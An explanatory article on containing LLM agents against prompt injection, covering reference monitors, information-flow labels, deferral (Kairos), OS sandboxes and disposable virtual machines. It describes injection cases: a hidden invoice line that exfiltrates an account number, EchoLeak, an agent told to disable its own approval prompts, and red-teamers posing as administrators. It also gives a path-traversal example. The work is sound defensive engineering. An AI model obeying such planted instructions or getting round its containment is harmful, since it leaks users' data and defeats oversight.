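# Containing AI agents that read untrusted documents: reference monitors and isolated virtual machines

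## Agents, injected instructions and the two containment designs

An LLM agent is a large language model (LLM) that an ordinary program runs in a loop. The program carries out the actions the model outputs, such as reading a file, running a command or sending a message. Many agents read web pages, emails and documents written by people the user has no reason to trust. These people can hide instructions in the text, and the model may follow them as if they came from the user. Security researchers call this prompt injection. Engineers who use containment accept that an injection will eventually succeed, and they limit what the agent can do when that happens by using controls outside it.

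There are two designs for containing an agent that reads untrusted documents, and an operator can combine them. In one, a reference monitor checks every request the agent makes to read, write or send data, and blocks those its rules forbid. In the other, the agent's program opens untrusted documents in a separate virtual machine (a simulated computer) that holds none of the user's data, and deletes the machine afterwards. Both ideas come from operating systems and are more than fifty years old.

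### One input for requests and documents

A language model only produces text. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes the loop that turns this text into action as six steps. The agent receives a standing prompt from its developer and a request from its user. It may then fetch background material from a database, and the model may reason in writing about what to do next, though some agents skip both. The model then writes a tool call, which names a tool and gives the values to pass to it. The agent's program executes the call and adds the result to everything the model has read so far, and the loop begins again. When a model "sends an email", it writes a request and the program sends the email, so the request can be checked before it is carried out.

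Ordinary software takes different kinds of input through different interfaces, but an agent keeps everything in a single context, the text that the model receives on each turn. The developer's rules, the user's question and a stranger's web page follow one another in that context, separated only by markers that are also text.

David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, traces prompt injection to the way language models work in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025). A model predicts the next token, a word or a piece of one, from all the tokens before it, and nothing in that process separates instructions from data. He compares this with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a web form. Developers can prevent that attack by sending their own command and the form's contents to the database separately,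 so that the database engine never reads the contents as a command. Language models have no separate channel for data. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) draws a similar contrast with computer memory, which also holds code and data side by side, but the operating system can mark an area of memory as data, and the processor will not execute anything in it.

Developers can train a model to ignore instructions in documents, or scan the documents first. *ClawMMU* (2026), which presents a design for protecting agents' memory, says both measures lower the attack rate but do not guarantee protection. David C advises relying mainly on safeguards that contain no language model and limit what the system can do.

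### Alice and the invoice

Suppose Alice asks her agent to summarise an invoice that a supplier emailed to her. The agent also holds her account number, which it needs for other jobs, and has a tool that fetches web pages. Somebody has added an instruction to the invoice, in white text on a white background, to append the account number to an outside web address and fetch that page.

The program reads the invoice and adds its text, including the hidden line, to the model's context. The model now has Alice's request, her account number and the attacker's instruction in one input. It writes a tool call for the fetch, and the program carries it out. The web address contains the account number, so the attacker can read it in the server's log whether or not the server returns a page. Alice gets her summary, which may be good, and notices nothing. This case adapts an example from *On the Relative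 Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026). That example uses the email itself as the document.

Security engineers call a tool like this one a sink, because data can reach an outsider through it. Less obvious features, such as image loading, can also be sinks. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) uses the EchoLeak attack as a test case. In that attack, an email instructed Microsoft 365 Copilot to put the user's data into the address of an image in its answer. The program that displayed the answer then fetched the image, sending the data with the request.

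Alice can lose her number only if the agent has private data, reads text from outside, and can communicate with the outside. The developer Simon Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta", and SC Media, a trade publication, uses the phrase in its advice on containing agents. Removing any one of the three stops the theft, but people want agents that have all three.

It is hard to say how often an agent will meet such text, but Google has looked for it on the public web. For *AI threats in the wild* (April 2026), Google searched several snapshots of Common Crawl, a public archive that stores two to three billion pages a month. Malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, though Google gives no absolute number. It found little sophistication in the injections, which included pranks, attempts to make AI assistants recommend a business, notices to keep AI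 readers away, and only a few attempts to steal data.

*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) provides an independent count of injections. It examined 1.2 billion addresses from the October 2025 crawl and confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or roughly eight pages in a million. Site operators had placed about four fifths of them themselves. Both studies began by searching for known phrases, so they miss injections that are worded differently. Web archives also exclude private documents, such as an invoice in Alice's inbox. The counts measure the background level on the open web and are of little use for estimating the risk to someone an attacker has targeted.

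### A monitor that refuses the request

The reference monitor comes from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the United States Air Force by a panel studying how people with different security clearances could share one computer. Until then the main defence had been to keep outsiders away from the machine, which does not help against what the panel called a malicious user, someone who is authorised to use the system and can write programs for it. The panel therefore wanted a mechanism inside the system to check each attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the user may do.

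One can picture the list as a table. Each row stands for a user or a program, each column for a file, device or program, and each cell holds the permitted kinds of access, such as reading or writing. In the companion volume, Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, credits the concept to earlier work by Lampson and by Graham and Denning. The panel's lasting contribution was to attach three requirements to the mechanism:

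- It must be tamper-proof, since whoever can alter the mechanism can switch off the protection.
- The system must invoke it on every access. If some programs may skip the check, they become "part of the security apparatus" and have to meet the other two requirements themselves.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Otherwise nobody can know that it works in all cases.

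The panel had a practical reason for the third requirement. The Air Force had seen teams of hired attackers break into every system they tried. Anderson argues that even a failed attempt would have proved little, because an attack can reveal flaws but cannot show that none remain. He also applies the requirements to a commercial system of the day, the Honeywell 635 with its operating system GCOS III. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but it suspended the check whenever the operating system acted on the user's behalf, which breaks the rule about checking every access. The operating system could itself be considered the monitor, but at the time it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far more than anyone could verify.

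In Alice's case, the monitor checks the model's tool calls before they run. It needs only one simple rule, which blocks the agent from fetching web pages once it has read anything from outside. The model may still follow the hidden line and write the request, but the monitor denies it and no request leaves the machine. Alice still gets her summary, because summarising an invoice doesn't require a fetch. The same rule would have blocked her own task if she had asked the agent to read the invoice and then look up the supplier's website.

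Anderson's table alone would not have produced this result. Alice may read her account number and fetch web pages, so an agent acting in her name may do both, which lets the stranger use her rights through the agent. David C therefore calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a program with wide powers that someone with fewer powers induces to act for them. A monitor for agents therefore has to consider what the agent has read as well as whom it acts for. David C quotes a rule of thumb from an exchange between Willison and another developer that a model processing a party's text should keep only that party's privileges.

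A flaw catalogued in 2025, which Dongol also uses as a test case, shows why a monitor must be tamper-proof. It affected the agent mode of GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant. An attacker could put a comment in a source file telling the agent to disable the prompts that asked the user for approval and then execute a command. The prompts were a kind of monitor, but the agent could turn them off because it could write to the setting that controlled them.

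### A separate machine for the document

A virtual machine is a computer implemented in software. It has its own operating system, files and apparent hardware, and programs inside it run as they would on a physical computer. The machine that runs it is called the host, and the system inside it is called the guest. A program called a hypervisor divides the host's processor, memory and devices among the guests and keeps the guests isolated from each other. A container is a lighter alternative that gives a group of programs a private view of files and the network. These programs still use the host's kernel, the core of its operating system, so a flaw in the kernel may let them escape the container.

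Products use both designs. When Claude writes code in the claude.ai chat service, Anthropic runs it in a container on its own servers, with a file system that lasts for one session. The container uses gVisor, software that puts an extra layer between the programs and the host's kernel. Kaspersky's *Why AI agents need an iron curtain* describes IronCurtain, an open-source project by the researcher Niels Provos that puts the agent inside a virtual machine, away from the user's accounts.

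The design for untrusted documents isolates the document rather than the whole agent. If the whole agent moved into a virtual machine with the account number, the number and the hidden instruction would still be in the same context. For Alice's invoice, the program instead starts a secondary virtual machine and copies only the invoice into it. Software in that machine reads the invoice and writes a summary, which the program takes out before deleting the machine. The hidden instruction may well take effect inside, but the account number is not there, and if the operator has also closed the machine's network connection, there is no way to send anything. Either condition alone would protect the number. The attacker may still control the summary, so the agent has to treat it as untrusted, a problem that designs with two separate models try to solve.

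Anderson's panel already knew of this approach and named two IBM systems that used it, CP-67 and VM/370. Their control program gave every user a virtual machine with an operating system of the user's choice. In the second volume, Anderson calls their facilities for sharing files rather primitive. Sharing remains the weakness of this approach, because separation is easy only when people have nothing to exchange, and Alice wants something back from the machine that read her invoice.

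Both designs rest on a trusted computing base, the set of all parts that must work correctly for the security guarantee to hold. For the monitor, the base includes the monitor and its rules, the program that executes the tool calls, and the operating system and hardware underneath. For the secondary machine, it includes the hypervisor, the host's hardware, and the code that moves the invoice in and the summary out. The main attraction of containment is that neither base includes the language model. In Dongol's analysis of monitored agents, the attacker can even choose which text the model obeys and when.

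### Secrets, actions and answers

Alice faces three risks. Her account number may leak, which is a failure of secrecy. Her agent may do something she never asked for, such as make a payment, which security researchers call a failure of integrity. Or the agent may give her a wrong summary without leaking anything or doing anything unusual.

A system can protect secrets without preventing unwanted actions, and vice versa. Dongol gives an example of each. An assistant that answers every email with its user's calendar can fall for an instruction to answer twice. The second reply reveals nothing new, but nobody asked for it. In EchoLeak, Copilot leaked a secret through an image in its answer, though including images was normal behavior for it.

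The word "unwanted" needs a precise definition. Dongol considers an agent told to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email, and four versions of that invoice. The first is ordinary. The second contains an instruction to change the payee to Mallory, the third an instruction to pay Mallory £1,000 as well, and the fourth an instruction to delete Bob's email afterwards. Dongol counts an action as a breach only if an agent that never obeys hidden instructions could not have acted the same way on any other invoice. The extra payment and the deletion are therefore breaches. The change of payee is not, because such an agent would also have paid Mallory if the invoice had named Mallory in the payee field. This test is consistent, although the payer still loses the money. It places the fault in the task, which let the invoice decide who receives the payment.

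The third aim is a correct answer. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) states this aim in terms of a user's query *q*, a document *d* and the agent's decision *J*(*q*, *d*). The decision may depend only on what in *d* is relevant to the task, and must stay the same whatever else an attacker adds. An automated reviewer fails this requirement if self-praise in a paper leads it to give a better mark, and a shopping agent fails it if a planted product review steers it towards a bad purchase.

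Surveys do not always separate this aim from the second. Of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues collected, 30 target integrity, four confidentiality and two availability, meaning that they try to slow or stall the agent. But their integrity class includes manipulated review scores and misinformation as well as hijacked actions. The difference matters for containment. If the hidden line in Alice's invoice makes the model report £900 where she owes £9,000, the monitor has no forbidden request to refuse, and the secondary machine returns the wrong figure just as it would the right one.

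## How a reference monitor decides on file and tool requests

A reference monitor acts only on requests, so its protection depends on how it handles each one. Dongol models the monitor as a state μ and a decision. The decision takes the state, the tool *t* and its arguments *args*, and returns a response *r* and a new state μ′:

decide(μ, *t*, *args*) = (*r*, μ′), where *r* is Allowed or Denied

In practice, most of the work lies in turning a request into something the monitor can compare with its rules.

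### One file request, step by step

Suppose Alice's agent asks to read `/home/alice/invoices/march.pdf`. The monitor must first identify who is asking. An agent usually runs under its user's account, so the monitor has to treat it as a separate party with fewer rights than the user. If several people share an agent, the monitor must also tell them apart. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports that a red team (a group that attacks systems to test them) found agents that held individual users' credentials but answered any authorised user of the internal network.

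Next, the monitor has to find the real file, because one file can have many names. The path `/home/alice/invoices/../bank/account.txt` begins with the invoice folder but leads out of it, since two dots mean "go up one level". A symbolic link, a small file that points to another file, can also lead out of the folder without its name showing this. The monitor must therefore follow all dots and links before it checks the policy. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* gives this advice for Claude Cowork, the company's desktop agent for office work, because a link inside a permitted folder could otherwise give the agent access to files outside it. The monitor must also open the same file it checked, or an attacker could change the link between the check and the opening.

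The monitor then looks for rules that match the real path. Rules can overlap, so the policy language has to define which one takes precedence. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* shows a configuration for Claude Code, its programming agent, that blocks reads of the user's home directory but allows reads of the current project inside it. This works because the rule with the narrower path takes precedence. ARM, the monitor presented in *Causality Laundering* (2026), instead sends each request through four layers of checks, and a denial from any layer is final. A careful policy also denies any request that no rule covers, because nobody can list every request an attacker might try.

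If the rules permit the request, the monitor passes it on and the agent receives the file. Whether or not it permits the request, the monitor records who asked, what they asked for, and what it decided. ARM's log is hash-chained: each entry includes a fingerprint of the one before, so later tampering can be detected. A model can also report an action it never requested, which is a problem ordinary logs do not have. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), which analyses agents as operating systems, treats "claimed but not performed" as a separate state that the log and the monitor have to detect.

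Finally, the agent receives the outcome, which in Dongol's model is only "ok" or "fail". Products often return more, because an explanation helps the model find a permitted way to finish the job. For example, when Claude Code's sandbox blocks a connection, the result names the refused host. But details can also help an attacker, and *Causality Laundering* is about information that leaks through denials. If the error for a forbidden file differs from the error for a missing one, an injected instruction can make the agent try a list of names and learn which files exist.

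### A policy for Alice's agent

Alice's agent needs to read her invoices and save summaries. The following policy permits that and nothing else:

```
read     /home/alice/invoices/**     allow
write    /home/alice/summaries/**    allow
connect  any address                 deny
other    anything                    deny
```

The two asterisks stand for everything inside the folder. As before, the agent has Alice's account number in its context, and the March invoice contains a hidden instruction to send the number to an outside address. The agent makes three requests:

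| Request | Origin | Matching line | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read `invoices/march.pdf` | Alice's task | First | Allowed |
| Connect to the attacker's address, with the account number in the link | Hidden line in the invoice | Third | Denied |
| Write `summaries/march.txt` | Alice's task | Second | Allowed |

The monitor does not have to recognise the second request as injected, because it would refuse the same request from Alice.

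The third line applies to the agent's tools. If the model runs on a provider's servers, the agent's program still has to send the invoice there, and Anthropic points out that isolation does not change what goes to the model.

The policy also doesn't restrict what the agent writes in the output folder. The hidden line could cause the model to put the account number in the summary, and the monitor would allow the write. This does no harm while the file stays on Alice's machine. But if she adds a rule that lets the agent upload summaries to her accountant's file-sharing service, where other people can read them, each request would comply with the policy, yet together they would expose her account number.

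### Judging a request by what came before

A monitor without memory decides from the request alone, so it must give identical requests the same answer. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) shows why this is not enough, using an example in which an agent has permission to upload reports to GitHub's servers. The agent uploads a harmless status report, overwrites it with a confidential inventory, and uploads it again. The two upload commands are identical, but a monitor should allow the first and deny the second because the file now contains the inventory.

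Tether, their monitor, does this by keeping a secrecy label for each file, *L*(*f*), and one for everything the agent has read, *C*. With two labels, Public and Sensitive, the symbol ⊔ means "the stricter of the two". Leaving aside the labels of folders, the main rules are:

- When the agent reads *f*, *C* becomes *C* ⊔ *L*(*f*).
- When the agent writes to *f*, *L*(*f*) becomes *L*(*f*) ⊔ *C*.
- When a command copies *f* to *g*, *L*(*g*) becomes *L*(*f*).
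- The monitor permits an upload of *f* only if *L*(*f*) is Public.

After the copy, the report carries the label Sensitive, so the second upload fails. It would fail however many temporary files the inventory passed through, because each copy gets the label. The same rules would close the gap in Alice's policy. Once the agent has read a file with her account number, *C* is Sensitive, and so is every summary it writes afterwards. But the monitor would then also block uploads of summaries that don't contain the number. Tether's design allows such false alarms. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as containing data from the first.

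The monitor also has to find out what a command does, since a one-line command can start a script that opens dozens of files. Tether runs the command in a temporary layer over the file system and records its system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system's kernel, while a proxy holds back network requests. If the policy permits everything the command did, Tether applies the file changes and forwards the network requests; otherwise it discards them. On recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks, Tether blocked every attack within its scope and wrongly stopped 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs. Its scope excludes attacks that violate no rule about data flow and attacks that go through databases or background services, which Tether can only block entirely.

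Other monitors store different information. The one in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) can base a decision on which model call produced a message or which approvals preceded an action. The rule from Alice's first example withdraws the web tool once the agent has read outside text, so the monitor only needs to store whether that has happened. Dongol has proved a theorem about such rules.

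### Where the check can sit

Many developers write the check into the prompt, telling the model to avoid risky actions, and some add a second model to judge the first. These checks can consider the user's wording and its purpose, but any text that sways the model also sways the check. NVIDIA's testers defeated them by claiming to be administrators or to be debugging, by moving towards the forbidden request over many turns, and by asking for ordinary-looking steps with hidden effects, such as installing a software package that can run its own code during installation.

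A check inside each tool is ordinary code, so persuasive text does not affect it. It receives the tool's name and arguments, so it can tell a payment from a calendar entry. However, each tool enforces only its own rules. *Ring-0 by Default* reports experiments on three deployed agents in which boundaries held in one tool and not in the next. Developers can reduce this problem by sending all calls through one gateway, as ARM does, but a gateway still inspects only the call. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that once a tool starts another program, the application cannot monitor what that program does. An attacker can therefore use a permitted tool that runs scripts to perform a forbidden action.

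An operating-system sandbox puts the check underneath all of these programs. The kernel applies it to the process and to every process it starts, whichever tool began the chain. Four mechanisms are common:

- Seatbelt, which is part of macOS, checks a process's file and network operations against a profile of rules.
- Bubblewrap, on Linux, starts a process with its own view of the file system, in which other folders are missing or read-only. It can also cut the process off from the network.
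- Landlock, also on Linux, lets a program give up access to files and some network operations for itself and its descendants.
- Seccomp filters Linux system calls by type and simple arguments. It cannot judge a file path, because the call passes only the memory address where the path is stored.

These sandboxes restrict access by path and connection, without any information about what the user wants done. Like containers, they share the host's kernel, so a process can escape by exploiting a kernel flaw. A process can also get around the restrictions by using a program outside the sandbox. For example, Anthropic warns that a process with access to the control socket of Docker, a program that manages containers, effectively has access to the host.

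A monitor at the edge of a virtual machine runs outside the guest's kernel, so an attacker who takes over that kernel still faces the check. To get past it, the attacker needs a flaw in the hypervisor or a channel that the operator forgot to route through the monitor. In Cowork, the user chooses which folders the guest can reach, and each can be read-only, writable, or writable without deletion. Anthropic first ran the whole agent inside the guest, where no outside process could grant it an exception. Start-up failures in that design left the product unusable, so Anthropic moved the agent's main loop to the host and kept code execution in the guest.

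A monitor at the edge of the virtual machine has less information about what an action is for than a tool gateway does. When an agent makes a payment, the gateway receives "pay £900 to this supplier", while the monitor at the edge receives only a web request to a bank.

### Claude Code's defaults and NVIDIA's controls

Claude Code has an operating-system sandbox, built on Seatbelt for macOS and bubblewrap for Linux, but the user has to switch it on. According to Anthropic's documentation, commands in the sandbox can write to the working directory, a temporary directory and any folder the user has added. They can read almost any file on the computer, including those that hold passwords and keys. The list of permitted network domains starts empty, and in the ordinary interactive mode Claude Code asks the user when a command tries to contact a domain that isn't on the list.

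Anthropic restricts both files and the network because a command could use a gap in one restriction to get around the other. A command with open network access could leak the user's keys, and a command with free write access could plant code that later runs with network access. Commands also cannot change Claude Code's own settings or certain other configuration files, even inside the working directory. Otherwise a command could grant itself permissions or add a hook, which is a script that Claude Code runs automatically, outside the sandbox, when a certain event occurs.

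The sandbox covers only shell commands. Claude Code's built-in tools for reading and editing files and fetching web pages follow separate permission rules, and hooks and local tool servers run with the user's full access. If Alice blocked access to her bank folder only in the sandbox settings, a shell command could not read it, but the built-in reading tool still could. To restrict all of these, she can run Claude Code itself inside a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox runtime.

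For convenience, Claude Code's defaults allow commands to run outside the sandbox in two cases. If the sandbox cannot start, for example because a package is missing, commands run without it. If a command fails inside the sandbox, the model can request a retry outside it. Depending on the mode, the user or a classifier decides whether to allow the retry, or it runs without a prompt. An administrator can turn off both defaults.

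In its *Practical Security Guidance*, NVIDIA's red team gives three controls for such agents as mandatory and six as recommended:

| Control | Level | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Block network access except to known destinations | Mandatory | Stops data theft and remote control of the machine |
| Block writes outside the workspace | Mandatory | Some files outside it, such as shell start-up scripts, run automatically and could carry an attack out of the sandbox |
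| Block writes to configuration files everywhere | Mandatory | These files can define hooks and tool servers, which often run unsandboxed |
| Block reads outside the workspace | Recommended | Protects secrets and hides information useful for further attacks |
| Sandbox the whole development environment | Recommended | Many products sandbox only the command line |
| Give the sandbox its own kernel | Recommended | Code in the sandbox can attack a shared kernel |
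| Ask for approval every time an action breaks the isolation rules | Recommended | A saved approval can cover a later attack |
| Supply only the secrets that a task needs | Recommended | Limits what a hijacked agent can use |
| Delete or rebuild the sandbox regularly | Recommended | Old sandboxes accumulate secrets and code |

Once switched on, Claude Code's sandbox largely meets the three mandatory controls for shell commands. It departs from the recommended controls because it leaves most files readable, shares the host's kernel and reuses approvals. When a user approves a domain, the sandbox allows access to it for the rest of the session, and the user can also save the approval for future sessions. NVIDIA rejects reusing approvals, but asking every time also has a drawback, because people stop reading prompts that appear too often.

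The team's later post, *Four Ways*, puts control over who may use the agent first. It also reports that network limits forced the testers to do everything through the agent, which made their attacks slower and less reliable. Even so, they sometimes got the agent to print credentials in the chat, which no network rule prevents. NVIDIA therefore recommends keeping long-lived secrets out of the agent's environment.

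### Kairos: delaying the decision

Even a monitor with a complete record of past events may lack the evidence it needs to decide on a request, because that evidence comes later. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that follows an online guide to set up a code repository. The guide tells it to install a hook that runs whenever someone saves a version of the code. Many legitimate guides do this, so refusing the file would break ordinary work, but allowing it might plant malicious code. The harm becomes evident only when the hook runs and sends the user's private key to a stranger.

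Hempel and colleagues use two results from the theory of monitors to explain the problem. Schneider showed that a monitor that can only allow or refuse actions can enforce only rules whose violation is visible in the events so far. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker showed that a monitor can enforce strictly more rules if it can also hold back an action and release it later. Kairos adds this option, so it can allow, refuse or defer an action.

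The agent itself needs no changes. It runs with all its tools in a small virtual machine with its own kernel. The user's working directory appears inside as a read-only base with a writable layer on top, and the real files stay untouched until Kairos merges the layer into them. A firewall sends all network traffic through a proxy on the host, which decrypts it for inspection. A tool call and a script written by the agent therefore reach the monitor as the same kinds of event, namely file operations and network requests. From this arrangement Hempel and colleagues derive three guarantees, which they call confinement:

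- Every effect that leaves the virtual machine passes the monitor.
- No effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it.
- No refused effect ever becomes visible outside.

Confinement holds even if the attacker fully controls the model, provided that the virtual machine, the monitor and the host work correctly and every channel is monitored. Kairos logs and releases all traffic to the model's provider, so confinement also depends on the assumption that the provider does not collude with the attacker. This assumption does not cover an attacker who has an account with the same provider and plants that account's key in the document.

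Deciding which effects to release is harder, and Kairos offers weaker guarantees for it. The operator's policy lists trusted sources, sensitive data and what each destination may receive. The monitor first refuses any effect that a rule forbids. For the rest, it checks whether the values that control the effect, such as a recipient, a web address or a command, came from a trusted source, and whether the destination may receive the data. If both hold, it releases the effect, and otherwise it defers.

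Since the monitor cannot inspect the model's internals, it traces values by comparing text. It treats a recipient as trusted if the same string, ignoring capitals and spaces, appeared in the user's task or another trusted source. An agent can defeat this comparison by deliberately encoding a secret before sending it. Hempel and colleagues claim only to confine such an agent.

A deferred file write goes into the writable layer, where the agent can use the file as if it were real. When a deferred request sends data, the proxy holds it and gives the agent a stand-in reply. The proxy cannot do this for a request that fetches a page, because the agent needs the page's contents, so Kairos decides on these requests before sending them. Everything the agent does after a deferral belongs to one transaction. At the end of the task, or earlier if something has to leave the machine, a separate language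 model without tools reviews the transaction. This model can release or refuse only what the policy deferred, and a human reviewer can take its place.

If the reviewer approves, Kairos applies the changes and sends the held request. Otherwise, it discards them. Kairos cannot erase these steps from the model's memory, so it tells the agent which effects were cancelled and instructs it to continue with the user's task. In the example, the policy blocks the hook from sending the key, and because of that attempt the reviewer discards the hook as well.

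Hempel and colleagues tested Kairos on three benchmarks that plant injections in an agent's tasks. AgentDojo simulates office, banking and travel applications, AgentDyn uses tasks whose steps emerge only along the way, and AutoDojo rewrites each injection over six rounds to get past the defence. The figures compare an agent without defences to one with Kairos:

| Benchmark | Injection cases | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
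|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 629 | 47.0% → 2.7% | 82.7% → 85.1% | 59.8% → 69.5% |
| AgentDyn | 560 | 37.8% → 1.7% | 53.3% → 51.7% | 55.5% → 37.1% |
| AutoDojo | 389 | 52.4% → 8.8% | 66.7% → 65.3% | not reported |

The agents in the table used GPT-4.1, GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini, which are all old models now. Hempel and colleagues ran each configuration once. Results were similar for two other models on AgentDojo, where attack success fell to 1.3% and 2.4%.

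A further test on AgentDojo measured the policy without deferral: Kairos refused every effect that it would otherwise have deferred to the reviewer. Attack success hardly changed, but the agent completed only 42.7% of its tasks when there was no attack. The protection therefore came from the policy's rules, and deferral allowed the agent to complete more tasks. In harmless runs, the policy released 83% of effects on its own, and the reviewer wrongly refused only one.

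Deferral worked less well on AgentDyn, where later steps often depend on a held action. Tasks kept 90% of their usefulness when they continued past one held action and 62% when they continued past two or more. The attacks that still succeeded on AutoDojo exploited tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document, so the reviewer treated the document's instructions as the user's.

Kairos adds about 1.9 milliseconds to a file operation and 1.2 to a network request, which is negligible compared with the time a model takes to answer. The reviewer's calls increase the number of tokens by 17.7% in harmless runs and 33.6% under attack.

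The timings come from the real virtual machine, while the protection figures come from benchmarks that simulate their tools inside one program, so no file operation or network request crosses a boundary. Hempel and colleagues wrote an adapter that turns each simulated tool call into an event for Kairos, and their policy specifies which argument names the destination and whether the action is reversible. At the edge of a virtual machine, the monitor would have to work without tool names and arguments, and the policy could express fewer rules. More decisions would then fall to the reviewing model, which reads the attacker's text. No one has measured how well Kairos protects an agent under those conditions, and Hempel and colleagues note that doing so would require a benchmark whose actions have real effects on a system.

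## Opening untrusted documents in a separate virtual machine

A monitor has to check every request an agent makes after reading a hostile document. Opening the document in a secondary VM leaves the monitor less to check, because the agent that holds Alice's account number never opens her invoice. How well this protects Alice depends on what the secondary VM shares with the rest of her system and how hard it is to break out of.

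### From clean image to deletion

The host starts the secondary VM from a clean image, a file that contains an operating system and the software for reading documents. The guest can read but not change the image, and everything it writes goes into a temporary layer. Starting an operating system for every document would be slow, so some services save a snapshot of the memory of a machine that has already started, then launch copies from it. The trade publication InfoQ (2026) reports that Amazon Web Services (AWS) does this for Lambda MicroVMs, a service that can run code written by AI models.

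Alice's program then copies the invoice, and no other file, into the secondary VM. It must not open the invoice first, because extracting the text or making a preview on the host could let a malicious file attack the host's software. The program also passes in a task, such as "give the supplier, the amount and the due date". The task must not contain anything secret either, because it will be in the same VM as the hidden line.

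Next, a reader in the guest opens the invoice. The reader can be an ordinary program that extracts the text or a language model that writes a summary. Many models run only on their providers' servers, which the guest cannot contact because it has no network connection. The operator can either install a smaller model in the guest or have the host relay the guest's requests to the provider. A relay gives the guest a narrow channel to the outside and becomes part of the trusted computing base.

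The host should also limit the reader's time and memory. Otherwise a document that makes the reader run forever, or that unpacks to an enormous size, could slow down the whole computer without escaping the virtual machine.

The reader writes its result to an agreed place, and Alice's program collects it. An attacker may have chosen every character of this result, so the code that collects it must handle any input safely.

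Finally, the host stops the guest and deletes its memory and temporary layer, which removes any program that the invoice installed. The operator should use a new machine for each document, even when two documents come from the same supplier. If one machine read Alice's March invoice and then her April invoice, a hidden line in the March invoice could falsify the summary of the April one.

### Disposable machines in Qubes OS

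People used disposable virtual machines for suspicious files before there were LLM agents. Qubes OS is a desktop operating system that divides a user's work among virtual machines called qubes, such as one for banking and another for email. According to Qubes OS's *How to use disposables*, the user can choose "Open in disposable" on any file, and the system creates a new machine for that file alone. The system destroys the machine when the user closes it.

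The Qubes OS project recommends using disposable virtual machines to view untrusted files away from trusted ones and to visit untrusted websites without the login cookies from earlier sessions. An agent that reads attachments and web pages needs both protections.

A disposable can also turn an untrusted PDF into an image that is safe to view. A PDF may contain scripts and attachments, but the image contains only pixel colours, so code that attacked the PDF viewer stays in the disposable. The conversion would also remove the hidden line from Alice's invoice, since white letters on a white background become white pixels. It would not remove an instruction in visible type, which many models can read from an image.

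When a user edits a file in a disposable, Qubes OS passes the changes back to the qube the file came from. This is convenient for filling in a form. But software in the disposable produced the changed file, so that file deserves no more trust than the original.

Qubes OS's *Disposable customization* warns that a compromised template can compromise every disposable VM made from it. Users should therefore keep risky additions, such as untrusted browser plugins, out of important templates. Similarly, the operator should build the image for an agent's secondary VM from trusted software and never save a used machine as the new image. Qubes OS also lets users set disposable VMs to start without a network connection, which the project suggests for opening untrusted files.

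### What the boundary isolates

Suppose Alice's invoice contains both code that exploits a flaw in the PDF reader and the hidden line addressed to the model. If the code works, the attacker controls the reader and perhaps the whole guest. The guest contains the invoice and a short task, but no other files or passwords, and any change the code makes lasts only until the host deletes the machine. If the hidden line works, the attacker gains access to the same things by persuading the model. The virtual machine's boundary therefore limits the damage from both attacks, even if nobody detects them.

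Isolation in a virtual machine does not control the content of the returned text. The reader's summary could end with an instruction for Alice's agent to forward her last bank statement. Her program would put the summary into the agent's context, which also contains the account number. The injection would then reach the main agent even if the virtual machine worked correctly. NVIDIA excludes manipulated output from its sandbox guidance and treats it as the user's responsibility. A secondary VM therefore needs strict limits on what the reader may return.

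### What the machine shares with its host

In *The impact of memory safety on sandboxing*, Gaynor separates two things that a sandbox can do. It can take away a privilege, such as the ability to read files, so that a program cannot use it even when an attacker controls the program. It can also reduce the amount of kernel code that the program can call, in case that code contains a flaw. An operator who sets up a secondary VM makes both decisions. The first depends on what the operator connects to the guest:

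- **Folders.** A host folder that the operator mounts in the guest appears there as if it were local. The guest can then read everything in it. If the folder is writable, the guest can also leave something behind that survives its own deletion. Anthropic warns that an injection in a mounted workspace or in an agent's memory files returns every time the agent starts. Copying in a single file avoids both problems.
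- **Network.** A guest with a connection can send out whatever it has read. A list of permitted destinations narrows this risk, but data can also leave through a permitted destination. A machine that only reads documents usually needs no connection, and if the operator gives it no network device, code inside has nothing to switch back on.
- **Credentials.** An injected instruction can use any password or access token in the guest. Anthropic keeps Cowork users' credentials on the host and gives the guest a token with reduced rights for one session, which it can revoke without affecting the user's own.
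- **Display.** To show a guest's window, the host has to process images and other data from the guest, and flaws in the code that does so can let an attacker out. A reader that returns text needs no screen.

Guests can also share parts of the processor, including its cache, a small and fast memory. Programs that use the same cache can sometimes learn about each other's data by measuring how long their own operations take, which security researchers call a side channel. AWS's *The EC2 approach to preventing side-channels* explains that virtual machines rented by different customers never share the processor's first two levels of cache. For Alice's invoice, a side channel matters less than a mounted folder would, because a program in a machine without network access has few ways to send out what it learns.

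### The whole agent or only the reader

Several products run their agents with a virtual machine or container, but few of them isolate the untrusted document from the agent's private data. It makes a great difference to Alice which part of the system sits inside the boundary:

| Inside the boundary | Example | What a hidden instruction can reach |
|---|---|---|
| The whole agent | First version of Claude Cowork | The agent's context, its tools and any folder shared with the guest |
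| Only the code that the agent runs | claude.ai, second local version of Cowork | The agent's context and its tools, though the code it runs stays inside |
| Only the reader | Secondary VM for one invoice | One document and the task that came with it |

In the first two arrangements, Alice's account number and the hidden line are in the same context, so the operator still needs a monitor to control where the agent can send data.

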